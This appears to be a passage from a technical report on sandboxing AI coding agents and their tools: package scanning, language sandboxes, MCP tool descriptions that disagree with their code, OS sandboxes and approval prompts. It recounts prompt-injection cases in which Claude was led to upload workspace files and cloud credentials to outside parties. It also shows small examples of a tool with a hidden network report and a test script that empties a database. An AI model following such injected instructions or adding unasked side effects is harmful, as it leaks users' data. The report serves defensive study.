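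Farrag's results are good evidence that models can tell whether a short program does what its requirement asks. They are weaker evidence that models can detect unwanted effects, because a program can meet its requirement and do something else as well. Both versions of "count_rows" return the correct number of rows. A current model would probably notice the network request in a function this short, but it might miss one in a dependency it never opened.

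*An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (Ryan, Khalil and colleagues, 2026) is closer to this problem. The study asked 13 models whether Python packages were malicious and, in a separate task, which of 47 known signs of malicious behaviour each malicious package contained. It scored the answers with F1, which combines the share of malicious items a model finds with the share of its alarms that are correct, and has a maximum of 1.

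The models' average scores ranged from 0.40 to 0.99 on the first task. They found most of the malicious packages but often flagged safe ones too. Identifying the specific behaviour was harder, and their overall score was 0.48. The models recognised distinctive patterns in code but missed behaviour that was suspicious only in context, and they did worse on longer packages.

These scores may not carry over to current practice. The models were mostly small, and the only proprietary one was GPT-4.1, which is far behind today's best. But the test was easy in some respects, since half the malicious packages had 36 lines of code or fewer and none of the safe ones had more than 260. The first task also used only 10 malicious packages and 93 safe ones, or about nine safe packages for every malicious one. Ryan and colleagues estimate that the ratio in Python's public package index is about 73 to one,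 so a larger share of alarms would be false in real use. They recommend using models to select packages for a person to examine.

People also find generated code hard to review. In *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), a survey of developers who use coding agents, 51% said it was hard to spot problems in plausible-looking code, and 55% had difficulty with large changes or changes to several files. Of 202 developers, 69% agreed that line-by-line review could not keep up with the code agents produce. These are opinions rather than measured error rates, but they suggest that much generated code is only partly read. A script that an agent writes, runs once and discards may not be read at all.

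### Sandboxes inside the language

A language's runtime (the program that runs the code, such as Python's interpreter) could block forbidden actions as they happen, rather than predict what the code will do. It could do this because ordinary requests to open a file or a connection pass through it. However, attempts to build this protection into existing languages have had serious problems.

Victor Stinner, a Python developer, spent three years on one attempt, pysandbox. It ran untrusted code inside CPython, the standard Python interpreter, and hid the parts that could do damage. People began to find ways out within three months of its first release in June 2010. In 2013, entrants in a security challenge found two more in under a day. Stinner fixed both, but soon announced that the design could not work. He gives two main reasons in *The pysandbox project is broken* (Stinner, 2013).

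Pysandbox ran untrusted code in the same process as the whole Python interpreter, whose core contained more than 126,000 lines of C. A single bug anywhere in that core could defeat the sandbox. Blocking the function that opens files was also not enough, because Python lets programs inspect their own workings in many ways, and unrelated functions offered indirect access.

The other reason was that each fix made the sandbox harder to use. Eventually, untrusted code could not perform basic operations such as deleting an entry from a dictionary, Python's standard lookup table. Stinner concluded that pysandbox was impractical for anything much more complex than arithmetic.

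In *The pysandbox project is broken*, Coghlan (2013) answered a recommendation to put the whole Python process inside an external sandbox by saying that Python's developers had been giving people this advice for quite some time. They still give it. In a later discussion, *Extending subinterpreters with sandboxing capabilities*, one developer said that it is feasible to sandbox Python as a language, but not to sandbox CPython from within. Another traced the problem to Python's principle of "consenting adults", the assumption that whoever writes the code can be trusted.

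Java's designers made the opposite assumption, that code should not be trusted by default. From its first release, Java had a component called the Security Manager, mainly to contain applets, the small programs that web pages once ran on visitors' computers. It let developers grant specific permissions to specific code, so one part of a program could read files while another part, in the same process, could not. A company could in principle have used it to give its own code network access while denying that access to a library that counts rows.

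This precision required changes throughout Java's standard library. *JEP 486* (Mullan and Buckley, 2024) reports that over 1,000 methods (functions) had to check for permission, and over 1,200 had to raise their own privileges at times. For example, a program with no permission to read files might request the local time, which Java works out using a file of time zones. The time library then had to assert its own permission to read that file. Tymshare's compiler had needed to do much the same when it wrote to STAT.

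Few developers ever turned the Security Manager on. According to Mullan and Buckley, most of those who did granted every permission to all their code, which defeated the purpose. Java's maintainers marked the feature for removal in 2021 and permanently disabled it in Java 24, released in 2025. Like Stinner, Mullan and Buckley recommend external sandboxes instead.

They also argue that most current attacks use malicious data rather than malicious code, and that the Security Manager offers little protection against such attacks. This is reasonable for traditional business software, whose code changes slowly and comes from known developers. It applies less well to agents, which constantly run new code that nobody has checked.

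### Recording what Python does

Python's developers later settled for a more modest goal, and since version 3.8 programmers have been able to add audit hooks. These are functions that the interpreter calls when a program does something notable, such as importing a module, opening a file or connecting to a server. A hook receives the event's name and details such as the file's path, and can record the event or stop it.

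Dower proposed the hooks to give security tools more context. A tool outside the process might report that something had started listening for network connections, but not what led to it. A suitable hook would record the connection that the second version of "count_rows" makes to stats.example.com.

*PEP 578* observes in its section "Why Not A Sandbox" that every past attempt to sandbox CPython had failed. The basic difficulty is that untrusted code must be denied certain abilities that the rest of Python needs. One is turning text into runnable code, which Python does whenever it imports a module from source.

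In 2021, Stinner wrote that the organisers of a hacking contest had built a challenge that used the hooks as a sandbox anyway, leading to several reports to Python's security team. A later change to Python's documentation, *Clarify in docs that sys.addaudithook is not for sandboxes*, added a warning that malicious code can easily disable or bypass hooks added from within Python.

Dower argues that detecting an intruder matters more than early prevention, because blocked attackers tend to switch to methods that are harder to detect. That makes sense for a company that monitors its systems over weeks, but a record is less useful when the damage takes seconds, as it did at PocketOS.

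### Permissions for a whole process

The JavaScript runtimes Deno and Node.js can limit what an entire process can access. Deno gives a program no access to files, the network, environment variables or other programs unless the user grants it. The user can limit a grant to one folder or one web address. Node.js has similar controls, but they apply only if the user turns them on.

| | Deno | Node.js |
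|---|---|---|
| Restrictions by default | On | Off |
| Environment variables | Blocked unless the user allows them | Always readable |
| Starting other programs | Blocked unless the user allows it | Blocked unless the user allows it |
| Compiled extensions | Blocked unless the user allows them | Blocked unless the user allows them |
| Developers' advice on untrusted code | Add further layers of protection, such as a virtual machine | Do not rely on these permissions to contain malicious code |

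The Node.js column describes what happens once the user has turned the restrictions on, except in the first row.

These permissions can prevent harm. Suppose someone rewrites both versions of "count_rows" in JavaScript and runs them in Deno with permission to read only the sales file. The first version works as before. The second fails when it tries to contact the server, and the records stay on the computer. The user doesn't need to read the code or know which package the request came from.

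NodeSource makes a similar case for Node.js. Malicious code in a package could still read environment variables, but without network access or the ability to start other programs, it would have trouble sending them anywhere. Node.js' *Permissions* also describes an audit mode, which reports what the restrictions would block but still allows it, so developers can find out what a program needs before they enforce any limits.

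The protection has gaps, some of them deliberate. Node.js describes its permissions as a "seat belt" that keeps trusted code from using resources by mistake, and says malicious code can bypass them. NodeSource reports that flaws found in 2025 and 2026 let code get around both the file and network restrictions. Deno is more ambitious, but it enforces its permissions in the JavaScript layer, so they do not restrict compiled extensions or other programs the user has allowed. Deno advises treating permission to use either as equivalent to full access.

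Process-wide permissions also apply equally to every function in the process. In Deno, all code on the same thread (a single sequence of execution) has the same permissions. Developers can move untrusted code into a separate worker with fewer permissions, but they have to know which code to move. Suppose the sales script needs to send its total to the company's accounting service. The user has to allow connections to that service, and "count_rows" can then send every customer's name there too.

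## Tool descriptions and the effects of tool code

Like imported packages, an agent's tools contain code that can have effects users never see. The model chooses a tool by reading a short description in ordinary language, not the code, and that description may be wrong or incomplete.

### How a model chooses a tool

When an agent connects to an MCP server, the server sends a list of its tools. Each entry has a name, the arguments the tool accepts and usually a description of what it does. The agent program adds this list to the prompt, and the model picks the tool that seems to fit the task. The tools' code stays on the server, which may be another process on the user's computer or someone else's machine.

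MCP does not check a tool's description against its code. Developers can change a tool and forget to update its description, and some never write one. In *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026) found no description for 2,170 of 19,200 tools. Skills have the same weakness. In *Towards Secure Agent Skills*, Li et al. (2026) note that no mechanism keeps a skill's instructions within its stated purpose.

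Adam and colleagues illustrate the gap with the file-writing tool mentioned earlier, which also contacts a metrics service. This is a simplified version:

```python
@tool(description="Writes text to a file")
def write_file(path, text):
    metrics.send({"tool": "write_file", "bytes": len(text)})
    with open(path, "w") as file:
        file.write(text)
```

The model receives the tool's name, its description and its two arguments. The description is accurate but incomplete. The tool does write the file, but the third line also sends the tool's name and the length of the text over the network. A developer might add such a line just to learn which tools people use.

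An agent program can't enforce a rule such as "no network use with secret code" if it doesn't know which tools use the network. An accurate description would provide that information, but a model can still choose badly or follow an injected instruction.

### How much access tools use

Several studies have estimated what tools can do. Li, Li and colleagues (2025), in *We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP*, searched the code of 2,562 MCP servers for calls to functions that use files, the network or other system resources. Huang, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *My Credentials, Please*, started 4,806 servers and had a language model label them from summaries of their tools. Pandey, Singh and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Maliciousness*, had language models read the full contents of 6,309 skills from two marketplaces.

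| Type of access | MCP servers, Li and colleagues (2025) | MCP servers, Huang and colleagues | Skills, Pandey and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| Network | 56% | No figure | 31% |
| Files | 24% | 44% | 35% read, 31% write |
| Shell, processes or system settings | 48% | No figure | 50% (shell only) |
| Credentials | No figure | No figure | 13% |

These percentages are rough. The 2025 search skipped third-party packages, so it would miss a server that reads files only through a package. The study gives no error rate. Huang and colleagues did not measure how accurate their labels were either, and they sampled only servers they could install and run.

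The figures for skills describe what their contents would allow, which is more than a skill does in any one run. When Pandey and colleagues ran nearly all the skills in a sandbox, they recorded shell use for only 8%. They treat this as a minimum because a single run exercises only part of a skill. Three of the five researchers work for Metano Labs, which makes the scanner, and nobody outside the company has evaluated the results.

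A tool that fetches web pages needs the network, so access alone is not evidence of a fault. Access is more worrying when the tool's purpose doesn't explain it. Huang and colleagues found that 787 of the servers they studied (16.4%) could use files although the model had not classified them as file tools. Many of these servers probably had a good reason, such as saving their own data.

The researchers therefore tested selected tools directly. They placed fake credentials outside the folders each tool should need, then checked whether the tool could be made to go beyond those folders. They confirmed 150 cases in which it could. One was in Anthropic's server for Git, a program that tracks versions of a project's files. The server's tool for adding files to a project could also expose files from elsewhere on the computer, a flaw its developers have since fixed. The researchers used a model to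 help infer each tool's proper boundary, and they have not measured how often the model was right.

### How often descriptions and code disagree

*Don't believe everything you read* (Li, Ma and colleagues, 2026) compared the code of 10,240 MCP servers with their documentation. In about 13% of the servers, the documentation covered less than 80% of what the code could do. One server advertised read-only access to GitHub but contained a function that changed users' information. The most popular servers had no severe mismatches, but their documentation was less likely to match the code completely than that of obscure servers.

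This study's findings probably apply more to documentation than to the tool descriptions given to models, because it used README files and similar documents. A function missing from a README may still have an accurate tool description. The study also reports no error rate.

Shi and colleagues compared tool descriptions with the tools' code. They collected the 19,200 tools from 2,214 MCP servers written in Python, and 17,030 of the tools had both a description and code to compare. For each tool, their program extracted the main function, the other functions it called within the same project, and any sensitive library calls. They then used Claude Sonnet 4.5, an older Anthropic model, to check whether the description matched the code and, separately, whether it conflicted with the code. If the two answers were inconsistent, the model compared its explanations for each and gave a final answer.

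Asking both questions made a large difference. On a sample the researchers checked by hand, the model missed more than half the real inconsistencies when they asked only whether the description matched. When they asked only about conflicts, it found all the inconsistencies, but about a fifth of its alarms were false.

The full method flagged 1,907 tools, or 11.2% of those with a usable description, and 35% of the servers had at least one flagged tool. In the hand-checked sample, 8 of the 200 flagged tools were false alarms, and 5 of the 200 tools that the program had cleared were inconsistent. Shi and colleagues report this as 96% precision (the share of alarms that are correct) and 97.5% recall (the share of inconsistencies found).

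The recall figure is too high for the full collection, where cleared tools outnumber flagged ones by about eight to one. If one cleared tool in 40 is inconsistent, as in the sample, the program missed about 380 inconsistent tools. Recall would then be about 83%, and about 13% of all tools would be inconsistent. These estimates are uncertain because they rest on only five misses.

The most common type of inconsistency, at 35%, was a description that listed something the code could not do. Undisclosed side effects were the main fault in 24.8% of cases, or nearly 3% of the tools checked. One tool was described as converting PDF files locally but uploaded them to an outside service. Another was described as only repeating a message but added a secret key from its environment variables. The number of tools with some undisclosed effect is probably higher, since the researchers counted each tool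 only under its main fault and did not follow code into every outside package.

A skill can also include a more formal list of the tools it uses, but this is not much more reliable. Some agents stop asking the user to confirm the listed tools, yet the list does not block unlisted ones. Only 770 of the 6,061 skills whose headers Pandey and colleagues could read had such a list. Of these lists, 59% left out something the skill could do and 22% matched the skill's contents. The format also has no way to declare access to credentials.

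Android developers, by contrast, have tended to request too many permissions. Pandey and colleagues attribute the difference to enforcement. An Android app can't use a permission it hasn't requested, so its developer has a reason to request many, whereas a skill can use the shell even if its author doesn't list it.

### Describing a tool from its code

A program can generate a tool's description from its code instead of relying on the author's account. *AgentBound* (2025) does this for MCP servers by listing the permissions each one needs. Developers who reviewed the lists rated them 80.9% accurate and identified no missing permissions. One developer objected that a list allowed a server to read all environment variables when it should get only the ones it used.

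Adam and colleagues also start from the code, but their design makes a separate decision for each tool call. Static analysis begins at the tool's main function and follows the code to every operation that could have an effect. It mainly looks for familiar library functions, such as those that write a file or send a web request. System calls would be less informative because the same one can write to a file, a network connection or another program. If a tool makes low-level calls directly, the analysis has to reject them or assume a very broad effect.

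The result is a synopsis, a short summary of the tool's possible effects and the inputs that influence them. The synopsis for "write_file" has three entries:

| Input | Possible effect |
|---|---|
| The path | Writing to the file system |
| The text | Writing to the file system |
| The text | Sending data over the network |

The last entry shows the metrics report. The tool sends only the text's length, but the length depends on the text, so the analysis still records a flow of information from the text to the length.

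The server provides this synopsis when the agent program connects. Whenever the model requests a tool, a policy engine in the agent program checks the synopsis against the user's current policy before the call goes ahead. One example policy allows only network use by default. It also lets a tool write in the workspace folder if the user wants a file edited, and it withdraws network access if the session involves sensitive data. The same tool could therefore be allowed when the user is working on an open-source library but forbidden when the user is working on a company's secret code.

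The policy engine is an ordinary program, so instructions in injected text can't make it allow a call. But its decisions are reliable only if the synopsis describes the code the server is running. A malicious server could supply the synopsis of a harmless tool and run something else. Adam and colleagues propose using security hardware to verify the code, but their prototype, which consists of the analyser, a library of sandboxes and a modified agent program, doesn't include this.

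### Why static analysis rejects acceptable calls

Suppose the policy lets the "write_file" tool write only inside the workspace folder. A model calls the tool to create "workspace/test/tests.py", which the policy allows. A later call to change ".bashrc" breaks the policy because that file is in the user's home directory, outside the workspace. The shell runs the commands in ".bashrc" when it starts.

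The tool runs the same code both times and writes to whatever path it receives. Static analysis happens before either request and has to cover every possible one, so it can conclude only that the tool may write anywhere. A policy engine that relies on the synopsis alone must reject both calls, including the harmless one. Even a perfect analyser would have this problem, because the path is not in the code. This is separate from the theoretical limits on predicting what programs do.

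Adam and colleagues check the path inside the tool, immediately before the write, because a check by the agent program on the model's request would miss any change the tool then makes to the path. The tool's developer replaces the ordinary file-writing function with one that also takes a list of permitted locations and fails if the path is not among them. Adam and colleagues call this a fine-grained sandbox because it surrounds one operation rather than the whole server. Each call passes its own list, so a server can handle several requests at once under different policies.

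This relies on developers adding the sandboxes correctly, which the researchers don't assume. The analyser therefore checks whether each effect has a sandbox and whether the agent program's settings reach that sandbox unchanged. If an effect has no sandbox, the policy engine rejects the call unless the policy explicitly allows that effect. With a sandbox around its file operation, "write_file" can write to the workspace but not to ".bashrc". It still can't run in a session with sensitive code, because the metrics report has no sandbox and the policy forbids network use.

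Shell commands need a different approach because they run as separate programs. The prototype makes a command's file changes temporary and checks them against the policy when the command finishes. It also sends the command's network traffic through a local program that allows only approved domains.

### Three tests of the design

Adam and colleagues tested the prototype on three scenarios, using an existing MCP server for software development. Each scenario had a version in which the agent did only what the user intended and a version with an unwanted effect.

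In the first scenario, a developer asks the agent to test a connection to Anthropic's service, save an access key in the project's ".env" settings file and add instructions to ".bashrc". In the unwanted version, the model guesses the wrong folder and puts the key there.

In the second scenario, a developer uses the same server for an open-source library and a company's private application. The unwanted version adds the hidden metrics report to the server.

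The third is the GitHub example from earlier. The copied file is again called ".env", and the agent publishes the project with Git's "push" command. The file contains a private key in the unwanted version and a harmless debugging setting in the intended one.

The researchers compared their hybrid of static analysis and fine-grained sandboxes with three alternatives: no protection, Anthropic's sandbox around the whole server with a single fixed policy, and static analysis without sandboxes. Each cell below lists the result for the intended version first and the unwanted version second.

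| Protection | ".env" file | Sensitive code | Git push |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Allowed, allowed | Allowed, allowed | Allowed, allowed |
| One global sandbox | Blocked, blocked | Allowed, allowed | Allowed, allowed |
| Static analysis alone | Blocked, blocked | Allowed, blocked | Allowed, blocked |
| Hybrid | Allowed, blocked | Allowed, blocked | Allowed, blocked |

Only the hybrid allowed all three intended versions and blocked all three unwanted ones. The global sandbox stopped the agent from saving the key in the wrong folder, but its fixed policy also blocked the change to ".bashrc" that the user had requested, because changing that file is usually suspicious. It allowed network use and could not detect whether a transfer contained secret code or a key.

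Static analysis did well on the second scenario, where it only had to determine whether the tool could use the network. It failed on the first because it could not tell where the tool would write.

The results for the third scenario look the same for static analysis and the hybrid, but a user would notice a difference. With static analysis, the policy engine forbade all shell commands once the session contained the key, so the agent could not publish anything. The hybrid could hide the ".env" file from the push command and let the agent publish the rest of the project. Setting permissions for each call makes this possible, because the task as a whole needs both the file and the network, but the push doesn't need the file.

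### How far the results carry over

The experiment shows that the design can work, but it does not measure how often it would, because Adam and colleagues chose the six test cases to illustrate problems that their design addresses. They call the results preliminary and do not report how many acceptable calls the system would reject in ordinary use or how much it would slow a server down.

They also recorded sessions with two small Anthropic models and replayed the same messages under each form of protection. This made the comparison fair, but a recorded model can't react when the system blocks its request. A live model might ask the user for help or look for a workaround. In Goel's tests, for example, an agent kept trying to get around a filter.

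The hybrid also had better information than the global sandbox. The researchers assumed that its policies were correct and accounted for what the user wanted and whether a file contained a secret, while the global sandbox had to apply one policy throughout. Some of the hybrid's success therefore comes from the policies rather than the sandboxes. If a policy didn't mark the key in ".env" as sensitive, the hybrid would allow the agent to publish it. Who should set the policy for a task, and how, is a separate problem.

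Adapting the design to other servers could take considerable work. The researchers tested one server, written in Rust, and modified its tools to accept sandbox settings. Rust's strict rules make effects easier to trace than in Python or JavaScript, so an analyser for those languages would have to reject more acceptable calls to be equally safe. Python and JavaScript account for 97% of the servers that Huang and colleagues managed to run, although servers in other languages failed to start more often.

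The analysis also covers only code written in the tool's own language, so it can detect that a tool sends a command to the shell or a query to a database, but not what the command or query will do. Similarly, the prototype can restrict a tool's web access to certain domains, but this doesn't distinguish reading a social media post from publishing one when both use the same domain.

The effects of a database tool can depend heavily on permissions set outside its code. *MAP* (2026) describes an MCP server that reads only three tables of information about a database. Its setup instructions nevertheless recommend connecting as a superuser, an account with unrestricted access. Static analysis of the server would not reveal how much that account can do. If a tool lets the model influence the query, the database may carry out a deletion the server's developers never intended.

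Generated code is even harder to fit into this design. A tool's developer can add sandboxes and run the analysis before the tool is used, but when an agent writes a script and runs it immediately, no developer is there to do either. The agent program could analyse each new script, but unless the script used the sandboxed functions, the program would have to reject many acceptable scripts or put a boundary around the whole process.

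## What operating-system sandboxes restrict and what they cannot see

An operating-system sandbox restricts a program from outside while it runs, so it can confine generated code that nobody has analysed. It works the same way on compiled extensions and shell commands. But a sandbox only controls which files and hosts a program can reach, and can't check whether the program uses them as the user wanted.

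### Three kinds of boundary

When a program opens a file, the operating system checks whether the user's account has permission. A process-level sandbox adds a second check that applies to one process and any children it starts, and the request has to pass both.

On macOS, Claude Code and Codex use Seatbelt, a sandbox built into the system. The agent program starts a command with a list of rules attached, and the kernel (the core of the operating system, which handles system calls) refuses requests that break them. On Linux, both agents use bubblewrap, which gives a command a restricted view of the computer, for example one in which every folder except one is read-only. Codex also uses seccomp, a Linux feature that blocks selected kinds of system call. Seccomp can't enforce rules about particular files because it receives only the memory address where a path is stored and can't read the path.

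A container gives a program its own file system, list of processes and network settings, but the program still makes its system calls to the host's kernel. A virtual machine has its own kernel, which runs on simulated hardware. In its guide to isolating Claude Code, Anthropic describes virtual machines as the strongest separation.

| | Process-level sandbox | Container | Virtual machine |
|---|---|---|---|
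| What it isolates | Access to chosen files and hosts | The file system, processes and network | The same, plus the kernel |
| What it shares with the host | The kernel, installed programs and most readable files | The kernel and any folders the user shares | The physical hardware and any folders the user shares |
| What it costs | Very little time, but some tools don't work | Start-up time and a separate set of installed tools | A full system start-up and more memory |

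Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes two other drawbacks of virtual machines. Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work, originally ran entirely inside one, so it was unusable if the virtual machine failed to start. Anthropic therefore moved the agent program out and left inside only the code that the agent runs. Companies also found that their security software couldn't monitor activity inside the virtual machine. Administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this is no substitute for live monitoring.

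All three kinds of sandbox can have security flaws of their own, so developers sometimes run one inside another.

### One file write and one network request

Suppose Claude Code, with its sandbox on, runs a script that adds up the sales records and saves the result in "total.txt". The script makes a system call to open the file for writing. The kernel checks the file's full path, which is in the working folder, where both the account's permissions and the sandbox's rules allow writing. It then returns a file descriptor, which the script uses to write the total.

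If the script then tries to change ".bashrc" in the user's home directory, the sandbox's rules block the change even though the account has permission to make it. The script gets an error such as "Operation not permitted".

According to Anthropic's guide to the sandbox, a command can reach the network only through a proxy, a program that Claude Code runs outside the sandbox to pass on approved traffic. Suppose the script contains the version of "count_rows" that sends the sales records to stats.example.com. The function requests a connection to that host through the proxy, which looks for the name in a list of allowed domains. The list starts empty, so in an ordinary interactive session, Claude Code prompts the user for a decision.

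If the user agrees, the proxy looks up the host's address. It refuses to connect if the name resolves only to the user's own machine or to certain other local addresses, including the one for cloud providers' metadata services. Otherwise it opens the connection and relays the data, which by default it can't read because the script and the server encrypt it.

Most database drivers don't use the proxy, so they can't connect even to an allowed host. If the sales records were in a database, the user might have to run the script outside the sandbox with full access.

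### What a system call leaves out

To send data, a process makes a system call named "write" with three arguments: the number of a descriptor, the location of the data in memory and its length. As Adam and colleagues point out, the call is the same for a file, a network connection and a pipe, which is a channel to another program. A script might make these three calls:

```
write(3, rows, 5120)
write(4, rows, 5120)
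write(5, rows, 5120)
```

When a program writes data, descriptor 3 could refer to a backup copy of a sales file, 4 to a server connection, and 5 to a pipe to a program that sorts the rows. The kernel records what each descriptor refers to, but someone reading a list of the calls would have to find the earlier calls that opened the descriptors. Sandboxes usually check access during those earlier calls, when the program supplies a path or an address. Later writes to the same descriptor go ahead without another check.

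Even when a program opens a resource, much of what matters is missing:

| Request | What the sandbox can check | What it can't tell |
|---|---|---|
| Open ".bashrc" for writing | The process and the path | Whether the user asked for this change |
| Connect to github.com | The process and the host's name | Whether the script will download a library or publish a private key |
| Open the sales file for reading | The process and the path | Whether the records are secret, or which part of the task needs them |

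A rule can therefore allow changes to ".bashrc" or forbid them, but it can't allow them only when the user wants them.

### Defaults in current agents

Anthropic introduced Claude Code's sandbox in October 2025. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* reports that the sandbox reduced approval requests by 84% in the company's own use, because commands inside the sandbox could run without approval. Fewer requests may reduce approval fatigue, in which users stop reading what they approve, but Anthropic gives no matching figure for harm prevented.

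The same post says that a compromised Claude Code can't steal a user's SSH keys, which give access to other computers. With the default settings, this protection depends on the network boundary, since sandboxed commands can read almost every file, including credential files. The sandbox also doesn't stop a key from reaching the model's provider if a command prints it.

Claude Code's sandbox is off by default, and on Windows it works only through a Linux layer. If the sandbox can't start, for example because a package is missing, Claude Code runs commands without it unless the user has chosen a stricter setting. The sandbox covers only shell commands. The agent's own tools for reading and editing files follow separate permission rules, and local MCP servers run with the user's full access. The University of Vermont's *Claude Code Permissions & Sandboxing* warns that the most common mistake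 is to assume the sandbox restricts everything Claude reads.

Codex's sandbox is on by default. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, commands have no network access and can write only in the workspace and temporary folders. OpenAI's *Sandbox* explains that programs Codex starts, such as test runners, inherit these restrictions. In the cloud version, which uses containers, secrets are available during setup, but OpenAI removes them before the agent starts work.

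Wiesen writes in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that before Codex had a sandbox on Windows, users there had to approve nearly every command or give the agent full access.

Codex deliberately runs calls to trusted MCP tools outside its sandbox because these tools often need to connect to other applications or services, according to a 2025 change to its documentation, *Update README.md (#2564)*. Codex can send the sandbox's current rules only to servers that have opted in (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI MCP Sandbox-State Metadata*). Under an October 2026 update listed in *Michael Bolin*, a log of code changes from Navigara, it is still up to servers to pass these rules on.

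Claude Cowork automatically runs generated code in its virtual machine. The code can access only two folders on the user's computer, the workspace folder the user selects and a folder of Claude's settings. The user's stored credentials stay outside the virtual machine. Local MCP servers originally ran inside it, but Anthropic moved them out because they were hard to audit there and some needed to work with programs on the host.

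| | Claude Code | Codex on the user's computer | Claude Cowork |
|---|---|---|---|
| Default setting | Off | On | On |
| Files that code can read | Nearly all | Files in general, unless the user blocks them | Those in the shared folders |
| Files that code can change | Those in the working and temporary folders, with some exceptions | Those in the workspace and temporary folders, with some exceptions | Those in the shared folders, unless they are read-only |
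| Hosts that code can contact | None until someone approves them | None until someone approves them | Those on a list, which includes Anthropic's own service |
| Local MCP servers | Outside the boundary | Outside the boundary | Outside the boundary |

The Claude Code column describes the sandbox once the user has turned it on, except in the first row.

As the last row implies, none of these sandboxes would restrict the "write_file" tool or its hidden metrics report if a local MCP server provided the tool. Claude Code users can restrict such a tool by running the whole agent, including its servers, in a container, a virtual machine or a separate sandbox program that Anthropic supplies.

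### Fixed policies and changing tasks

A sandbox usually applies the same rules to every task. If a user loosened the fixed policy in Adam and colleagues' experiment to allow the requested change to ".bashrc", the file would be exposed during every other task too.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives examples of rules that depend on where data came from, such as a company's rule that one customer's data must never go to another customer. An ordinary sandbox can't enforce this rule in a process that handles both customers' records and can contact both customers. A developer could run a separate process for each customer, each allowed different files and hosts, but would have to plan that division in advance.

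Odersky and colleagues note that an agent can read a secret in one permitted step and send it out in a later one. Preventing this without blocking either step requires tracking the secret between them, which some programming languages can do through their types.

When a fixed policy blocks work people need to do, they make exceptions. If a command fails in Claude Code's sandbox, Claude may ask to rerun it outside the sandbox. Users who have already allowed that kind of command may not be asked again, because the earlier permission also covers the retry. Users can also exempt particular programs. Docker, which runs containers, doesn't work inside the sandbox, and a broad exemption for it gives the agent access to everything Docker can do.

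Claude Code can now adjust some permissions for each command. In its automatic mode, Claude lists the hosts a command needs, and a separate model reviews the list and the command together. Access to any additional hosts ends when the command finishes. This is closer to least privilege than a permanent list of allowed hosts, but it depends on one model to request the right access and another to notice when a request is unreasonable.

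### Harm through permitted files and hosts

Even a precise list of allowed hosts can permit data theft. Cowork's list included Anthropic's own service, which the product needs to work. An outside researcher showed that a malicious file in the user's workspace could exploit this, using hidden instructions and an attacker's access key for the service. Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the workspace and uploaded them to the attacker's Anthropic account.

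The proxy allowed the connection because the destination was on its list. Anthropic writes, "The sandbox worked perfectly, and yet the data was exfiltrated." As with Tymshare's compiler, the permission was too broad, because it let the code contact a host without distinguishing between the accounts on it.

Anthropic fixed this by adding a proxy that reads requests to its service and accepts only those with a token issued to that virtual machine. The fix works because Anthropic knows which account each session should use. A general-purpose proxy would need similar information about every service on its list.

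The PocketOS deletion raises a similar problem. Claude Code's default sandbox would have let the agent read the file containing the Railway token. It would normally have asked the user before the agent first connected to Railway, but if the user had already allowed that host for routine work, the deletion request could have gone through without another prompt.

Claude Code can also optionally hide credentials from commands. A command receives a placeholder instead of the real token, and the proxy substitutes the token only in requests to approved hosts. This would prevent code from sending a usable Railway token to an unapproved host, but the code could still use the token at Railway to delete a database.

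Files inside the boundary are also at risk, because an agent allowed to edit a project's files can usually delete them too. Cowork reduces this risk by letting people share a folder as read-only, or with permission to change files but not delete them.

### Files that outlive the sandbox

A sandbox restricts a process while it runs, but the files the process leaves behind may later influence programs with more access. Suppose an agent edits a project's tests from inside a sandbox, and the developer then runs them from an ordinary terminal. The tests, including any harmful code the agent added, run with the developer's full access.

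If a sandboxed command could edit Claude Code's settings, it could add an MCP server that Claude Code would later start outside the sandbox. Claude Code's sandbox therefore protects those settings, along with shell start-up files, editor settings and the scripts that Git runs automatically. Codex similarly makes its own settings folder and Git's data read-only, even inside the workspace.

These lists can't cover every risky file, because an agent has to change source code to be useful, and someone will eventually run that code. The lists can also miss files that don't exist yet. On Linux, Anthropic's separate sandbox program sets its list of protected files at startup, so it doesn't protect settings in a project the agent downloads later. After an agent has worked unattended, Anthropic recommends reviewing the folders the agent could write to.

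An agent can also trust files that were in a project before the agent started. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws that let code run before the user had agreed to anything. In the most direct case, Claude Code ran a command from a downloaded project's settings at start-up, before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Anthropic changed Claude Code to ask first.

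### Limiting damage without understanding the code

Despite these limits, a sandbox handles many cases where source review fails. Like Deno's permissions, it can block a network request from any package in the program. It also restricts compiled extensions and other programs, which Deno's permissions don't. A sandbox that blocked unknown hosts would have stopped the malicious version of litellm from sending stolen credentials to the attackers' server, even before anyone discovered the attack.

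Injected text can't make the kernel ignore a rule, but this protection is weaker if the agent program can exempt commands from the sandbox. In Cowork's original design, the whole agent ran inside the virtual machine, so it could not run a command outside it. Claude Code's agent program runs outside its sandbox, and an injected prompt or a careless approval can lead it to run a command without the sandbox's restrictions.

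A test at Anthropic in February 2026 shows why a boundary is useful even when an instruction comes from the user. A researcher sent an employee a prompt that looked like a routine request from a colleague. Its setup steps included an instruction for Claude to read the employee's Amazon cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. The employee ran the prompt in Claude Code, and Claude sent the credentials in 24 of 25 repeated trials. Defences that look for departures from the user's instructions could not detect this, because the user had supplied the prompt.

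Anthropic concludes that only limits on the network and files would have worked in this situation. Claude Code's default sandbox would have let a command read the credentials, but sending them to an unfamiliar host would have required approval. In an interactive session, the person asked to approve could have been the employee who had just pasted in the prompt.

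## Approval prompts and execution logs

A sandbox can't detect whether the user wanted an action, so agents often ask for approval first, and they keep a log that the user can check afterwards. But approval prompts and most agents' logs are mostly command text, which shows little about what a command does to files, other programs or the network.

### One request to run the tests

Suppose an agent has edited a JavaScript project and asks to run `npm test` to check that everything still works. Besides installing packages, npm can run commands that a project defines for itself. Here it finds the entry called "test" in the project's package.json file and passes that text to the system shell. One project might have this entry:

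```json
"test": "node --test"
```

Another might have this one:

```json
"test": "node reset-database.js && node --test"
```

Suppose the extra script in the second project empties whichever database an environment variable points to, so that the tests start with clean data. This is harmless if the variable points to a test database. If it points to the live one, the script deletes the company's records, even though the user approved the same two-word command as in the other cases.

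| | What the prompt shows | What the run may involve |
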